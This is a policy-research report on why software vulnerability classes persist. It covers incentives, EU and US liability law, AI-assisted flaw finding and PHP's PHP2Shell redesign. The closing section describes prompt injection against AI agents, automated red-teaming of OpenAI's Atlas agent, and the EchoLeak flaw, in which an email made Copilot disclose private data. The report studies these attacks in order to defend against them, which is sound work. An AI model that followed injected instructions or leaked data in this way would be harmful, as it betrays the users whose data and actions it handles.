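CISA renewed its call to eliminate whole classes of vulnerability in its August 2026 vulnerability review, which is also the source of this report's figures on stubborn weaknesses. According to Help Net Security, CISA said old mistakes survive because of companies' culture and because companies have been slow to adopt Secure by Design. It recommended that software makers eliminate common classes and publish roadmaps for the rest, and it listed practices that prevent each recurring weakness. It also warned that many exploited flaws involve several weaknesses, so makers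 should prioritize those that attackers commonly use together.

CISA did not explain in the review why years of voluntary pledges had achieved less than it hoped, or how it would overcome companies' reluctance to accept responsibility for their customers' security. Help Net Security noted that accepting this responsibility could suggest legal liability. CISA may also have fewer people to work on the problem. *CISA promises proactive defense in new strategic plan* (Geller, 2026) described the agency as still recovering from major workforce cuts when it published the plan in October 2026.

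The campaign's former leaders still work on software security, now outside government. Cable runs Corridor, which sells an AI platform for developing secure software. Lord and Zabierek joined the Institute for Security and Technology, a think tank, in 2025, and on 9 November 2026 they launched the Software Safety Institute, a non-profit. Zabierek and Lord (2026) say in *Introducing the Software Safety Institute* that it will measure the state of software security and try to change the market forces and policies that shape it. They argue that AI is now finding the same kinds of flaws that topped the lists 20 years ago, and that telling customers to patch faster can't keep up.

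The institute is still raising money and has published little. Its first podcast series is about the persistence of memory safety flaws. It has also responded to a government consultation on the National Vulnerability Database, which adds information to CVE records. The response, written with Nick Leiserson of the Institute for Security and Technology, argues that the database's main problem is that nobody is accountable for the quality of records when they are created, and that software makers should be held accountable for it.

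## Who would pay to remove a class, and can law change that?

Lord and Zabierek want their new institute to change the market forces behind insecure software. Researchers have studied those forces since about 2001 and mostly find that makers can afford to leave flaws in their products because customers bear most of the harm. The European Union has begun to shift some of the cost to makers, and the United States has considered doing so. The new laws are too recent to have had a measurable effect on any vulnerability class.

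### Who bears the loss

The Cambridge computer scientist Ross Anderson argued in *Why Information Security is Hard* (2001) that bad incentives cause at least as much insecurity as weak technology does. One example was cash machine fraud. When an American customer disputed a withdrawal, the bank had to prove the customer wrong. In Britain, Norway and the Netherlands, the customer had to prove the bank wrong, which was almost impossible. Banks there grew careless, and fraud eventually became widespread. American banks spent less on security but had much less fraud. Other differences between the countries may have contributed, but the comparison suggests that security depends a lot on who pays when it fails.

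Like the British cardholders, most software customers bear the losses themselves, because licences usually disclaim responsibility for them. If an attacker copies the online shop's database, the shop pays for the investigation and its customers deal with the fraud, while the software's maker pays for a patch. Economists call a cost that falls on outsiders an externality. Anderson cited Hal Varian's observation that people might happily spend $100 on antivirus software to protect themselves but not $1 to stop attackers using their machines against Amazon.

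Makers also gain by releasing early. Software often becomes more valuable as more people use it, and customers who have invested in one product find it costly to switch, so an early leader can keep the market for years. Anderson considered it perfectly rational in such a market to ship a product now and "get it right by version 3".

Rahul Telang and Sunil Wattal found in a 2007 study that a software maker's share price fell by about 0.6% on average when someone disclosed a flaw in its product, and by more when the maker had no patch ready. This reaction from investors gives a maker a reason to patch quickly, but much less reason to prevent the next flaw of the same kind.

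### What buyers cannot see

Customers might still pay extra for safer software if they could recognise it. Anderson borrowed the economist George Akerlof's example of a used-car market with 100 good cars worth $3,000 each and 100 bad ones worth $1,000 each. Sellers know which cars are good but buyers don't, so buyers offer $2,000, the average. Nobody will sell a good car at that price. Buyers soon notice that only bad cars are for sale, and the price drops to $1,000.

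Suppose two companies sell shop software, and one has spent heavily to make its compiler reject SQL queries built by joining strings. A retailer who tries both products sees no difference in their search boxes, so the careful company can't easily charge more and may not recover what it spent.

Independent testing could help, but Anderson pointed out that whether it does depends on who hires the tester. Under an older American scheme, the government evaluated products it meant to use itself. Under the Common Criteria, a later international scheme, the maker chooses and pays the evaluator, so the maker can look for whoever asks the fewest questions.

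### Shared components and old code

Many products contain the same free library, and no single company has enough reason to pay for improving it. Say a hundred companies each lose $50,000 a year to one class of flaw in a library, and removing the class would cost $1 million. If they split the cost, they would recover it in about ten weeks, but a company that paid alone would need 20 years, and the other 99 would benefit for free. Log4j was in roughly this position. Its volunteers had no resources for a security review that would have benefited thousands of businesses.

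Old code is a problem even when it has an owner, because a class-level fix often removes something that existing programs use. A maker whose update breaks its customers' programs may lose those customers. Anderson noted that companies such as Microsoft grew by appealing to outside developers, and that compulsory security features would have made those developers' work harder.

Engineers who have tried to remove vulnerability classes describe similar obstacles. *S3C2 Summit 2023-11* (Zahan, Acar and colleagues, 2024) summarises a private meeting of 13 practitioners from 11 companies. They thought a memory-safe language was easy to justify for a new project, but that rewriting a core library was hard to justify, especially when nobody knew of an immediate flaw in it. They suggested presenting security improvements to executives together with gains in speed. *S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (Rahman, Acar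 and colleagues, 2025) again describes such work as hard to sell to senior leaders. Both meetings were small and invitation-only, and the participants were probably more interested in security than most companies are.

### How long a maker waits to get its money back

An example with invented figures shows how much externalities matter. A maker spends $0.8 million a year patching one class of flaws. It could spend $6 million once to remove the class, which would prevent 80% of the flaws and cut the patching cost by 80%, or $0.64 million a year. The maker would recover its money in about 9.4 years.

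The same flaws cost its customers $5 million a year. If those losses also fell by 80%, the maker and its customers together would save $4.64 million a year and recover the $6 million in about 1.3 years. In general, if the maker bears a share *s* of its customers' losses, the payback time in years is

6 / (0.8 × (0.8 + 5s))

| Share of customers' losses that the maker bears | Maker's yearly saving | Payback time |
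|---|---|---|
| None | $0.64 million | 9.4 years |
| 10% | $1.04 million | 5.8 years |
| 25% | $1.64 million | 3.7 years |
| 50% | $2.64 million | 2.3 years |
| All | $4.64 million | 1.3 years |

A maker that wants its money back within three years would go ahead only if it bore at least 34% of its customers' losses. Because money saved in the future is worth less than money spent now, the payback time in the top row rises from 9.4 years to about 29 at a 10% annual rate of return.

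The example assumes that customers' losses fall in proportion to the number of flaws. If attackers turned to other kinds of flaw and losses fell by only 40%, payback with all losses counted would take 2.3 years instead of 1.3. The saving would also arrive more slowly if old flaws stayed in the code, as they did in Android.

On the other hand, the example may undervalue removing a class, because it treats every prevented flaw as equally useful to defenders. Anderson imagined a product with a million bugs, each of which takes an average of a billion hours of testing to find. An attacker who tests for 1,000 hours a year finds about one bug. A defender who tests for 10 million hours finds about 10,000 of the million, and so has only a 1% chance of having found the attacker's bug. (Anderson's paper gives 100,000 and 10%, which doesn't match its own figures.) But if half the bugs were stack overflows,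 Anderson suggested, a new compiler might remove them all. The defender would then have a 50% chance of having removed the attacker's bug without anyone finding it.

This helps explain Google's success with cross-site scripting. Google runs Gmail itself, so it bears more of the loss from an attack than a company that sells software for others to run.

### What Europe requires makers to build

The European Union's *Cyber Resilience Act* (2024) covers most software and connected devices that companies sell in the EU. The online shop's own website would normally fall outside it, but the packaged software that the maker sells to thousands of retailers would fall inside. Most of its rules apply from 11 December 2027. A maker will have to assess its product's security risks and design the product accordingly. Where the assessment shows that they apply, its duties include these:

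- sell the product without known exploitable vulnerabilities and with secure default settings
- limit the ways an attacker can reach it, and use mitigations to reduce the harm from an attack
- test it regularly and fix vulnerabilities without delay
- provide free security updates, for at least five years unless people will use the product for less time

The Act also requires a maker that finds a flaw in someone else's component to report it to the component's maintainer and share any fix it has written. This spreads the cost of patches, but it doesn't fund a redesign of the component.

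None of these duties mentions vulnerability classes, and a maker could comply with the ban on known exploitable flaws by patching them one at a time. But the general duty to design for the risks could require more. The maker must keep a record of the vulnerabilities it learns about and update its risk assessment where appropriate. If the record shows five SQL injection flaws in a year, a regulator could argue that patching the five was inadequate.

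Technical standards may determine how demanding the law is. If a product follows the EU's official standards, regulators presume that it complies. A standard that required parameterised queries throughout a product would push makers towards class-level fixes, while one that required only a documented review process would not. Most makers can assess their own products, but some, such as makers of firewalls, need an outside assessor. Anderson's warning about makers who choose their own evaluators applies to those who need one.

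The design rules don't cover products that reached the market before 11 December 2027 unless someone later modifies them substantially. A security update normally doesn't count as a substantial modification. But each new unit has to comply, so a router sold in 2028 must meet the rules even if its design dates from 2020.

### What Europe requires makers to report

The reporting duty began earlier, on 11 September 2026, and also covers old products. It applies when a vulnerability is actively exploited, meaning there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has used it in a system without the owner's permission. It also applies to severe incidents affecting the product's security, such as an attacker inserting malicious code into the update channel.

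After learning of either event, the maker has 24 hours to send an early warning and 72 hours to send a fuller notice. It must then send a final report, due within 14 days of a fix or mitigation becoming available for an exploited flaw, or within a month of the fuller notice for a severe incident. The reports go to a national response team and to ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency.

A researcher's private report of an unexploited flaw doesn't trigger the Act's duty to notify authorities. The Act's preamble says that makers should not have to notify them of flaws found through good-faith testing. Anyone may voluntarily report an unexploited vulnerability, or a near miss that could have become an incident. In October, ENISA's *Frequently Asked Questions* still left voluntary reports to "a future phase" of its reporting platform. ENISA released a new version of the platform in November, which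 may have changed this.

The law covers severe incidents that could damage a product's security, even if they haven't harmed anyone yet, so Europe does require reports of some close calls. It requires them only when something has happened to the product or its maker, such as a break-in at the company.

The authorities will therefore learn about a small and unusual sample of flaws. If attackers exploit roughly 2% of published flaws, as VulnCheck's 2025 count suggests, the compulsory reports will leave out about 98%. ENISA must prepare a report on trends every two years for a group of representatives of EU governments. Without many voluntary reports, that trend report, like CISA's KEV catalogue, could show which classes attackers use but not which classes makers keep producing.

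Even for exploited flaws, the final report need only describe the vulnerability, its severity and impact, the fix and any known attacker. Makers must give the likely root cause or type of threat for severe incidents, but not for exploited vulnerabilities. They don't have to say in either case whether they searched for variants. A few extra questions on the form would make the reports much more useful for studying vulnerability classes.

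Makers that break the main rules risk fines of up to €15 million or 2.5% of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher. The trade publication ComplexDiscovery pointed out that the article on penalties is not among the parts that took effect early. On a plain reading, a maker that ignores the reporting duty now would not face those fines until December 2027.

### Suing the maker in Europe

The EU's new product liability law, Directive (EU) 2024/2853, explicitly treats software as a product and applies to products placed on the market after 9 December 2026. Under its strict liability rule, an injured person has to prove that the product was defective and caused the damage, but not that the maker was careless. According to the preamble to the Cyber Resilience Act, a maker could be liable if its failure to provide security updates causes damage.

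Several provisions favour people harmed by familiar classes of flaw. A court can presume a defect if the product breaks mandatory safety rules meant to prevent that kind of harm, or if the maker refuses to disclose relevant evidence. A hacker's part in the damage generally doesn't reduce the maker's liability. The maker can escape liability if nobody could have discovered the defect with the scientific and technical knowledge of the time, but that would be hard to argue for SQL injection.

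However, the directive covers only some kinds of loss. Individuals can claim for death, injury, damaged property and the destruction or corruption of personal data. Ana may have a claim if an attacker wipes the family photographs from her home storage device, but the directive gives her no claim for the loss of privacy if an attacker only copies her orders from the online shop. The retailer can't use the directive to recover lost sales either.

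In the payback example, this probably leaves a maker of business software near the top of the table, bearing little of its customers' losses. A maker of home devices or medical equipment might move further down. Because a claim requires damage, the maker owes nothing under this law for a flaw that a researcher reports and the maker patches in time.

### The American proposals

The White House's March 2023 cybersecurity strategy proposed working with Congress on a law to make software companies liable when they fail to take reasonable precautions. The law would also stop companies with market power from disclaiming all liability by contract. Congress has not passed such a law. CISA's later pledge relied on persuasion.

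The government also tried to use its purchasing power. After a 2021 executive order, it began requiring software suppliers to attest that they followed certain secure development practices. CISA's standard form, published in March 2024, covered practices such as protecting the systems used to build software and checking for vulnerabilities before release. A supplier could truthfully sign it even if its programmers still built database queries by joining strings.

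In January 2025 President Biden ordered officials to prepare rules requiring suppliers to send CISA the evidence behind their attestations. President Trump cancelled that plan in June. In January 2026 the White House budget office withdrew the general attestation requirement, so each agency now decides what assurance to ask for and may still use the attestation form.

Government contracts seem to influence software makers. Participants in Zahan and colleagues' 2023 meeting said that the 2021 order had led companies to consolidate their build systems and standardise their engineering. They also thought that, without a broader effort, perhaps only companies seeking government contracts would prioritise safe languages. But at the meeting Rahman and colleagues described, participants warned that suppliers' own attestations about the security of their build systems could be misleading or fabricated.

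American makers can still have to pay for flaws that nobody is known to have exploited. In July 2025 the gene-sequencing company Illumina agreed to pay $9.8 million to settle allegations that it had sold federal agencies systems with security flaws and misrepresented their security. The Justice Department argued that Illumina's claims for payment were false whether or not anyone had broken in. It also alleged that the company had neglected security when designing its products. Illumina didn't admit liability. The case relied on the False Claims Act, which protects the government's money, so an ordinary customer couldn't bring the same claim for its own losses.

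### Would liability lead to class-level fixes?

Liability would give software makers a direct reason to take their customers' losses into account, and customers would no longer need to judge the quality of code they can't see. The cash-machine example is the best evidence here that liability can work, although banks had far better records of fraud than software makers have of attacks.

Open-source developers would be badly placed to pay. A volunteer who gives away a library earns nothing from it and can't control who uses it. Both European laws therefore exclude open-source software supplied outside commercial activity, and the American strategy opposed making the developers of open-source components responsible. A company that builds the library into a commercial product can be liable, which gives it a reason to fund improvements. But it might instead write its own version and introduce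 new flaws.

Strict rules could drive small makers out of the market and strengthen the companies that already dominate it, because a $6 million redesign might be routine for a large maker but impossible for one with 20 employees. The EU exempts small makers from fines for missing the 24-hour reporting deadline, but its design rules still apply to them.

Under negligence law, the customer must also prove that the maker was careless and that the carelessness caused the loss. This is hard when an attacker has combined three flaws in products from three companies. Carelessness should be easiest to prove for old classes with well-known remedies. A court could ask, much as Christey did in 2007, whether the mistake was well documented and whether a competent tester would have found it in minutes. Negligence law might therefore put more pressure on makers to remove SQL injection than to remove a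 subtle new class.

Liability could also make companies less candid. If a maker searches for variants and writes down what it finds, it creates evidence for the next lawsuit. It can avoid this by never looking, and then say it didn't know. The European ban on selling products with *known* exploitable vulnerabilities could also discourage searching, although the duty to test regularly limits this effect. Under EU law, notifying the authorities does not by itself increase a maker's liability, but the maker is still liable for any damage the flaw causes.

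### Safe harbours

A safe harbour would protect makers that follow specified practices from liability. The 2023 American strategy proposed one for companies that develop and maintain their software securely, drawing on guidance from the government's standards institute, NIST. Makers would know what they had to do, and honest ones could investigate their own flaws with less fear of a lawsuit.

If a written development process were enough to earn protection from liability, a company could follow the process and keep releasing the same kinds of flaw. In 2024 the lawyer James Dempsey proposed combining a safe harbour with a minimum standard for the product itself. A maker would be liable for specified, well-known weaknesses however good its process was, and the safe harbour would cover only flaws that are harder to detect.

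Dempsey's version seems more likely to lead to class-level fixes, because a maker could no longer treat a familiar mistake as bad luck. Lawmakers could go further and protect only makers that block listed mistakes automatically, for example with a compiler that rejects joined queries. But someone would have to keep the list current, and makers would have little reason to work on classes not on it.

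### When there might be evidence

Nobody has yet shown that any of these laws made a vulnerability class rarer. Europe's reporting duty is less than three months old, its design rules are a year away, and courts will probably need years to decide the first cases under the new liability directive. ENISA's first report on trends is due by September 2028, and the European Commission must publish its first evaluation of the Cyber Resilience Act by 11 December 2030. To measure any effect, researchers would need counts of flaws in each class from before December 2027, and would have to separate flaws in new code from older flaws that makers found because the law required more testing.

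## Does AI that finds flaws by the thousand help remove classes?

New laws may take years to change what software makers find worth fixing, but AI has already made flaws much easier to find and somewhat easier to patch. It may be starting to make redesign easier too. So far most of the effort has gone into patching individual flaws. The PHP emergency of October 2026 is a partial exception, because AI-assisted reports pushed the developers into a broad redesign that they had put off for two years.

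### What cheaper patches do to the case for redesign

In the earlier payback example, a $6 million redesign that prevented 80% of a class took 9.4 years to pay for itself if the maker bore none of its customers' losses. The table shows how AI might change that (all the figures are invented).

| What AI changes | Patching per year | Redesign | Payback time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | $0.8 million | $6 million | 9.4 years |
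| Each patch costs 75% less | $0.2 million | $6 million | 37.5 years |
| The same, and people find four times as many flaws | $0.8 million | $6 million | 9.4 years |
| The same, and redesign costs two-thirds less | $0.8 million | $2 million | 3.1 years |

A surge in discoveries strengthens the case for redesign, even when each patch is cheap. But part of the surge is a backlog of old flaws. In the stock-and-flow model, faster searching uses up that backlog, and the number of flaws found each year then falls back to the number that programmers add. A maker could reasonably decide to keep patching until the surge passes. That would be a worse decision if AI also led programmers to write more code with the same mistakes, or if attackers with the same tools found the old flaws first and the maker had to pay for the damage.

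### More reports than maintainers can handle

Volunteers and small foundations maintain much of the software that AI systems now scan. The Linux Foundation's *Linux Foundation and Industry Leaders Launch Akrites* (2026) quotes Varun Badhwar, head of the security company Endor Labs, as saying that fewer than 5% of the thousands of confirmed open-source flaws found in recent months had been patched. That share is very low, even allowing for the fact that Endor Labs sells help fixing such flaws and that some of them were probably too new to have been patched.

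The PHP Foundation's *Today's PHP Security Release, and How We're Strengthening PHP Security* (2026) reports that the security team for PHP, a programming language for building websites, had published 15 CVEs since 1 July. Over the same period, the team dealt with more than 100 other reports that were mistaken, repeated an earlier report or described something nobody could reproduce. AI helps the team check reports and group those with the same cause, but a person makes every decision and works on every patch. *How the PHP Security Team Handles Your Reports* (Daubois, 2026), written by a team member, describes the team as a small group of volunteers and paid contractors.

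Some argue that faster patching entrenches the practice of fixing flaws one at a time, because the people who answer reports are often the only ones who know the code well enough to redesign it. For example, a project's maintainers might have 60 hours a week between them. If checking a report takes three hours, fixing a genuine flaw takes another 12, and one report in eight is genuine, four reports a week take an average of 18 hours. Twelve take 54, which leaves six hours for everything else, including redesign.

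Automatic patching helps only so much because the maintainers spend most of their time on reports that don't lead to a patch. If AI wrote the patches and the maintainers needed only four hours to review each one, the twelve reports would still take 42 hours. Halving the time needed to check each report instead would reduce the total to 36 hours.

A project can also hire someone to do the neglected work. In September the PHP Foundation hired Daniel Scherzer to work through problems that don't qualify as vulnerabilities but make PHP sturdier when fixed. Barron (2026) noted in *Welcoming Daniel Scherzer to the Ecosystem Security Team* that such fixes prevent future reports. The job is short-term, though, and a grant pays for it.

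### Akrites and Gold Eagle

The Linux Foundation, a non-profit that supports open-source projects, launched Akrites in June 2026 to coordinate the response to flaws found with AI. Its founding members include Amazon Web Services, Anthropic, Google, Microsoft, OpenAI and several banks and telephone companies. Akrites has a shared response team and a single process for coordinated disclosure. According to the Linux Foundation, it will:

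- work with maintainers to fix flaws before attackers exploit them
- spare maintainers duplicate reports and conflicting patches
- help operators of critical infrastructure install the patches
- act as "maintainer of last resort" for important packages that nobody looks after

All four tasks concern individual flaws. The founders also promise to "harden" open-source software, which could include class-level fixes, but the launch announcement doesn't list finding recurring mistakes or replacing unsafe interfaces among Akrites's tasks. Pat Opet of JPMorganChase said the bank wanted to measure success by how many patches reach real systems. That is a better measure than the number of patches published, but a project could do well on it for years while its programmers kept making the same mistake.

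The fourth task may matter most for removing whole classes. The classes that companies have removed usually had an owner who could withdraw the unsafe option, and an abandoned package has no such owner. If Akrites takes over a package, it could convert the code to a safer interface as well as patch it, but it has promised only to deliver users fixes for the latest version.

The US government's counterpart is the Gold Eagle clearinghouse, part of the White House's response under Executive Order 14409. Its staff could count the flaws it receives by class, but for class-level fixes, someone would also have to be responsible for taking those counts to the people who control the languages and libraries involved. Ranking flaws by urgency only affects the order in which they are patched.

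### Can AI do the redesign?

The opposing argument is that the main obstacle to class-level fixes has been the effort of changing old code, and that AI can now do much of this tedious work. CodeMender, an AI agent from Google DeepMind, is an early test. It uses Google's Gemini models to trace the cause of a flaw, write a patch and check that the program behaves as before, revising the patch if the check fails. The Hacker News (2025) reported that Google had contributed 72 of CodeMender's security fixes to open-source projects in six months, some to projects as large as 4.5 million lines of code. Google DeepMind (2025) said that human researchers reviewed every patch before submitting it.

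Seventy-two patches in six months is about 12 a month, and the total doesn't distinguish instance fixes from wider changes. But Google also intended CodeMender to rewrite existing code so that whole classes disappear. Its main example is libwebp, a C library that many browsers and phones use to display pictures. CodeMender added notes to parts of the library that tell the compiler how much memory each pointer may reach. In simplified form:

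```
// before: nothing says how long the row is
void draw(char *row, int length)

// after: the compiler can check every access against length
void draw(char *__counted_by(length) row, int length)
```

The compiler then inserts a check wherever the code uses `row`, and the program stops if an access would go out of bounds. In 2023, attackers exploited a buffer overflow in libwebp to break into iPhones. Google DeepMind judged that the notes would have made that flaw, and most other overflows in the same parts of the library, impossible to exploit in this way. This comes close to a class-level fix for buffer overflows, and it didn't require translating the library into another language. It doesn't prevent the use of freed memory, and a bad calculation could still crash the program.

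Adding the notes is slow for a person, who has to read each function to find which variable holds the length. An AI agent can add them one function at a time and run the tests after each change. One library is a small sample, and Google chose it.

Google also uses CodeMender on single flaws. It has connected the tool to OSS-Fuzz, a service that tests open-source projects with unexpected inputs, so that maintainers receive a proposed patch along with each bug report. This should save them time, but each patch still fixes only one flaw.

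Translating C into a memory-safe language would go further. DARPA, the US military's research agency, is trying to automate this in its TRACTOR programme, short for Translating All C to Rust. Older tools can already translate C line by line, but the Rust they produce consists largely of `unsafe` blocks and keeps the original memory flaws. DARPA therefore wants Rust of the quality that a skilled programmer would write. To write safe Rust, the translator has to work out which part of the program owns each piece of memory, and C code doesn't record this. For example, a C function may return a pointer without indicating whether the caller should free the memory, and the translator may have to work that out from a comment or from what other functions do.

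A translation would therefore be better judged by how much of the new code is outside `unsafe` blocks and whether it still behaves like the original than by the number of lines translated. Google's AI-assisted rewrite of an image library was a fairly easy case, because image libraries have a narrow job and are simple to test. An operating system or a language engine would be harder, because thousands of other programs rely on its quirks.

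### PHP's two-year-old warning

PHP runs about 70% of websites. Its engine, the program that executes PHP code, is written in C, and in October 2026 its developers issued emergency patches for two critical flaws that became known together as PHP2Shell. Both were memory safety failures:

- CVE-2026-109618. Each visitor's request has a memory limit. When a request reached the limit, the engine abandoned whatever it was doing, which could leave half-built data in memory. Later code treated that data as complete.
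- CVE-2026-109619. The engine releases a request's memory when the request ends, but some of its longer-lived variables could keep pointing to the released memory. This is a use-after-free.

*php2shell*, by the security company Calif, traces the first kind of problem to 2004, when the researcher Stefan Esser found the first remotely exploitable flaw involving PHP's memory limit. It came up again in 2024, during PHP's first outside security audit in years. While fixing an issue the auditors had reported, a PHP developer noticed the first signs of what became CVE-2026-109618. Developers thought an attack might be possible but found no concrete way to carry one out, and flaws with a clearer impact took priority.

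Whittaker (2026), in *PHP had a rough week for security, but the pain isn't over yet*, says the 2024 bugs went unfixed because nobody could exploit them. The PHP Foundation gives a more complicated account, in which the security team developed several competing fixes that addressed the cause, but each would have broken existing programs, created new ways to overload a server, or required changes to many extensions that other people maintain. The team worked by consensus and couldn't agree. Work stopped and restarted for months, and the few people who understood the engine well enough had many other duties. The foundation calls the delay a "structural failure".

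AI-assisted research then changed the team's view of the danger. Calif began auditing PHP on 30 July 2026 as part of an OpenAI programme called Patch the Planet. On 11 August a Calif researcher reported a working attack with the same root cause as the 2024 problem. OpenAI independently reported that root cause on the same day, and the security company Wiz followed on 24 August. The foundation's security staff immediately made fixing the cause their top priority. They had known about the mistake for two years, so the AI-assisted research mostly added proof that it mattered. Psychologists would recognise this shift from seeing a disaster that did not occur to seeing one that almost did.

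The two same-day reports also count against Rescorla's premise that people searching separately seldom find the same flaw. Researchers who use similar AI models on the same popular code may find the same flaws more often than people used to, and attackers can use those models too.

### How the secret came out

Everyone involved agreed to keep quiet until the patches were ready, and the agreement held for about ten weeks. On 20 October the two CVE identifiers and screenshots of an attack tool spread online, and PHP's developers brought the release forward by a day, to 21 October.

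As far as anyone knew in August, these disclosures were near misses, but attackers later exploited the flaws. Tsai (2026), in *PHP2Shell*, quotes Amazon's finding that someone had tried the attack on one of its decoy machines on 17 October, four days before the patches. Amazon couldn't establish how the attacker had learned of it. Jones (2026), in *CISA, security researchers confirm successful exploitation of PHP flaws*, reported successful attacks by 27 October, and the security company Dream later described a campaign that had taken control of 25 servers. Whittaker had expected mass break-ins and attributes their absence to the secrecy and the difficulty of the attack.

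### A redesign in 390 files

The developers did much more than fix one instance of the memory-limit flaw. *What the PHP2Shell rumors got wrong, from inside the PHP security team* (Daubois, 2026) explains that under the old design, any C function in the engine that allocated memory might never finish, so programmers had to leave the data in a safe state before every allocation. Nobody could do that reliably throughout a large engine. Now the memory allocator records that a PHP request has exceeded its limit and lets the function finish. The engine stops the request soon afterwards, at a point where its data is complete. A second, higher limit shuts down the whole process if a request keeps consuming memory.

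The developers changed 390 files to do this. The change to the engine's architecture removes a common opportunity for a mistake and fits the definition of a class-level fix fairly well, though it protects only PHP. Daubois points out that C++ programs run a similar risk when they are short of memory, whereas Go and Rust programs normally just stop.

After two years of delay, the developers opened the proposed change on 25 September and finished it 23 days later, on 18 October. The foundation says it could put several people on the work full-time only because it had the money to pay them. A project with the same flaw but no foundation might have chosen the smallest patch that stopped the known attack.

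### Turning the second flaw into a rule

The PHP developer Sebastian Bergmann wondered whether a program could find the other flaws like the use-after-free. In *The wrong crash*, Bergmann (2026) reduced the class to one rule: when a request ends, no remaining variable should hold an address in the memory the request used.

PHP had more than 20,000 test files and a fuzzer, but they were badly suited to finding this kind of mistake. The fuzzer ran one request per input and carried nothing over to a second request, and some of the other tests used special builds of PHP that cleaned up memory differently from the version on real servers. Bergmann wrote an extension that lists a request's memory just before PHP releases it, then searches the engine's lasting variables for any that still point to that memory. In its first trial, the extension correctly distinguished versions of PHP with the October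 patches from versions without them.

Two weeks after the October release, the check found a previously unknown use-after-free in the code that stores time zones. The flaw scored 9.2 out of 10 for severity, and PHP's developers patched it on 19 November, along with others. Arghire (2026), in *PHP Patches Seven Critical RCE Vulnerabilities*, counted seven critical flaws, one of which resulted from an incomplete earlier fix for PHP2Shell. Four days later, Arghire (2026), in *phpAfterShell Vulnerability Revives PHP2Shell's Attack Path*, reported another related flaw.

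Bergmann's check is a very good way to look for variants, but each flaw it finds still needs its own patch. If PHP's developers ran it on every proposed change, it could also keep many new flaws of this kind out of the engine, as Cloudflare's scanner does with injection flaws. Programmers could still make these mistakes in C, and the check would miss any in code that the tests never reach.

The security team has also started changing its decision process to let a majority choose a fix and to encourage members to compromise. This may help remove the next class of flaw more than faster discovery would, because in 2024 the team had several possible remedies but could not agree on one.

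## Why are flaws in AI models mostly patched one at a time?

The developers of an AI model have no piece of code they can change to remove a common source of mistakes, as PHP's developers did by changing how the engine stops a request. The best-known flaw in these models is prompt injection, in which a model reads outside text, such as an email or a web page, and wrongly follows it as an instruction. It resembles SQL injection, but nobody has found an equivalent of the parameterised query that works inside a model. Developers have therefore mostly trained models to resist known attacks, or repaired one product at a time. Some research groups are instead trying to limit what a model can do after an attack succeeds.

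### Why a model can't keep instructions and data apart

A language model receives its whole input as one sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words. Suppose the online shop uses a model to answer customers' emails. The sequence starts with the shop's instructions and continues with Ana's email. The model then writes a reply by repeatedly predicting the next token from everything before it.

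The shop can put markers around Ana's email to label it as outside text, and the model's developer can train the model to prioritize the shop's instructions. But the markers are just more tokens, and although the trained model tends to follow the right text, no other part of the system forces it to.

David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, explained in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025) why models have no equivalent of parameterised queries, which prevent SQL injection. A database treats commands and stored values differently, so programmers can keep them separate. A model only predicts the next token and makes no such distinction, so developers have to impose one. He concluded that developers may never be able to prevent prompt injection as fully as parameterised queries prevent SQL injection.

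In practice, an AI agent (a model that can take actions such as sending email or buying things) also often needs to follow instructions it finds along the way. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a checkout page that tells visitors to log in first. An agent that ignored all outside instructions could never finish the purchase. The shop's database, by contrast, never needs to run a customer's text as a command, so banning that would disrupt almost nothing.

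### Where the usual responses fit

The five responses to the SQL injection flaw in the shop's search box have rough counterparts for AI models.

| Response to SQL injection | Closest counterpart for prompt injection |
|---|---|
| Fix that query | Change one product, for example by stopping an email assistant from opening links |
| Search for variants | Train the model on reported attacks and others like them |
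| Add a filter | Use a second program to screen what the model reads or writes |
| Offer a safe query interface | Offer developers a design in which outside text can't choose an agent's actions |
| Forbid the unsafe interface | Refuse to run agents built in any other way |

A programmer who fixes a flawed database query can check the new code, but a model retrained to resist one wording of an attack may still follow another.

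OpenAI has automated much of the work of training its browser agent to resist attacks. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an AI attacker that tries possible attacks on a simulated copy of the agent, studies the results and tries again. When an attack succeeds, OpenAI trains the agent against it and also looks for ways to improve its monitoring and other safeguards. One such discovery led to a new version of the agent, which OpenAI had released to all users by December 2025. OpenAI called the attacks behind that update a new class, but they were variants within one class, prompt injection.

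More training examples don't necessarily make a model safer. *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands* (Zorz, 2026) describes an experiment in which researchers retrained a small model separately on 7,132 working attacks found by one automated tool and 4,282 found by another. They then tried three unfamiliar attacks on 40 tasks chosen as known weak spots. At worst, attackers hijacked 19 tasks with the model trained on the larger collection and 11 with the other. The eight-task difference could be partly luck, but the model trained on more attacks had the weaker defence in three of the four set-ups tested. The researchers thought the larger collection consisted mostly of the same few attacks in different words.

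Sorting attacks by technique and rewarding the attacking tool for finding new techniques worked better. Standard attacks then succeeded less than 0.5% of the time, although attackers who revised their attempts about 250 times still succeeded on up to 10% of the 40 weak spots. Sorting by technique resembles grouping vulnerabilities by cause, and it seems a better use of near misses than just collecting them.

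Filters can miss harmful instructions or block helpful ones. Li and colleagues tested agents on 60 tasks where the right steps become clear only along the way and some outside instructions are helpful. The table gives results for agents using GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model.

| Defence | Tasks completed when not under attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| None | 53% | 38% |
| Marking outside text (Spotlighting) | 55% | 28% |
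| Filter (PromptGuard2) | 60% | 27% |
| Filter (ProtectAI) | 0% | 1% |

One filter let most of the danger through, and the other blocked so many harmless instructions that the agent couldn't complete any task. Li and colleagues chose older models partly because developers have probably trained newer ones on the standard attack used in the test. A newer model could therefore do well on the test without being able to resist unfamiliar attacks.

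Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2026) point out in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* that attackers repeatedly got past defences for image-recognition models and have since done the same with language models. Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist prompt injection, allowed 1.9% of attacks on AgentDojo, an older test, but 9.0% on Li and colleagues' test. Longer tasks may explain part of the increase, since they give an attack more chances to work.

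### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs told Microsoft about a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches a user's emails and documents to answer questions. The flaw, which they named EchoLeak, allowed an outsider to make Copilot disclose private company data by sending an email, without the user clicking anything. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, Microsoft completed its patch in May, and Aim Labs published its findings on 11 June.

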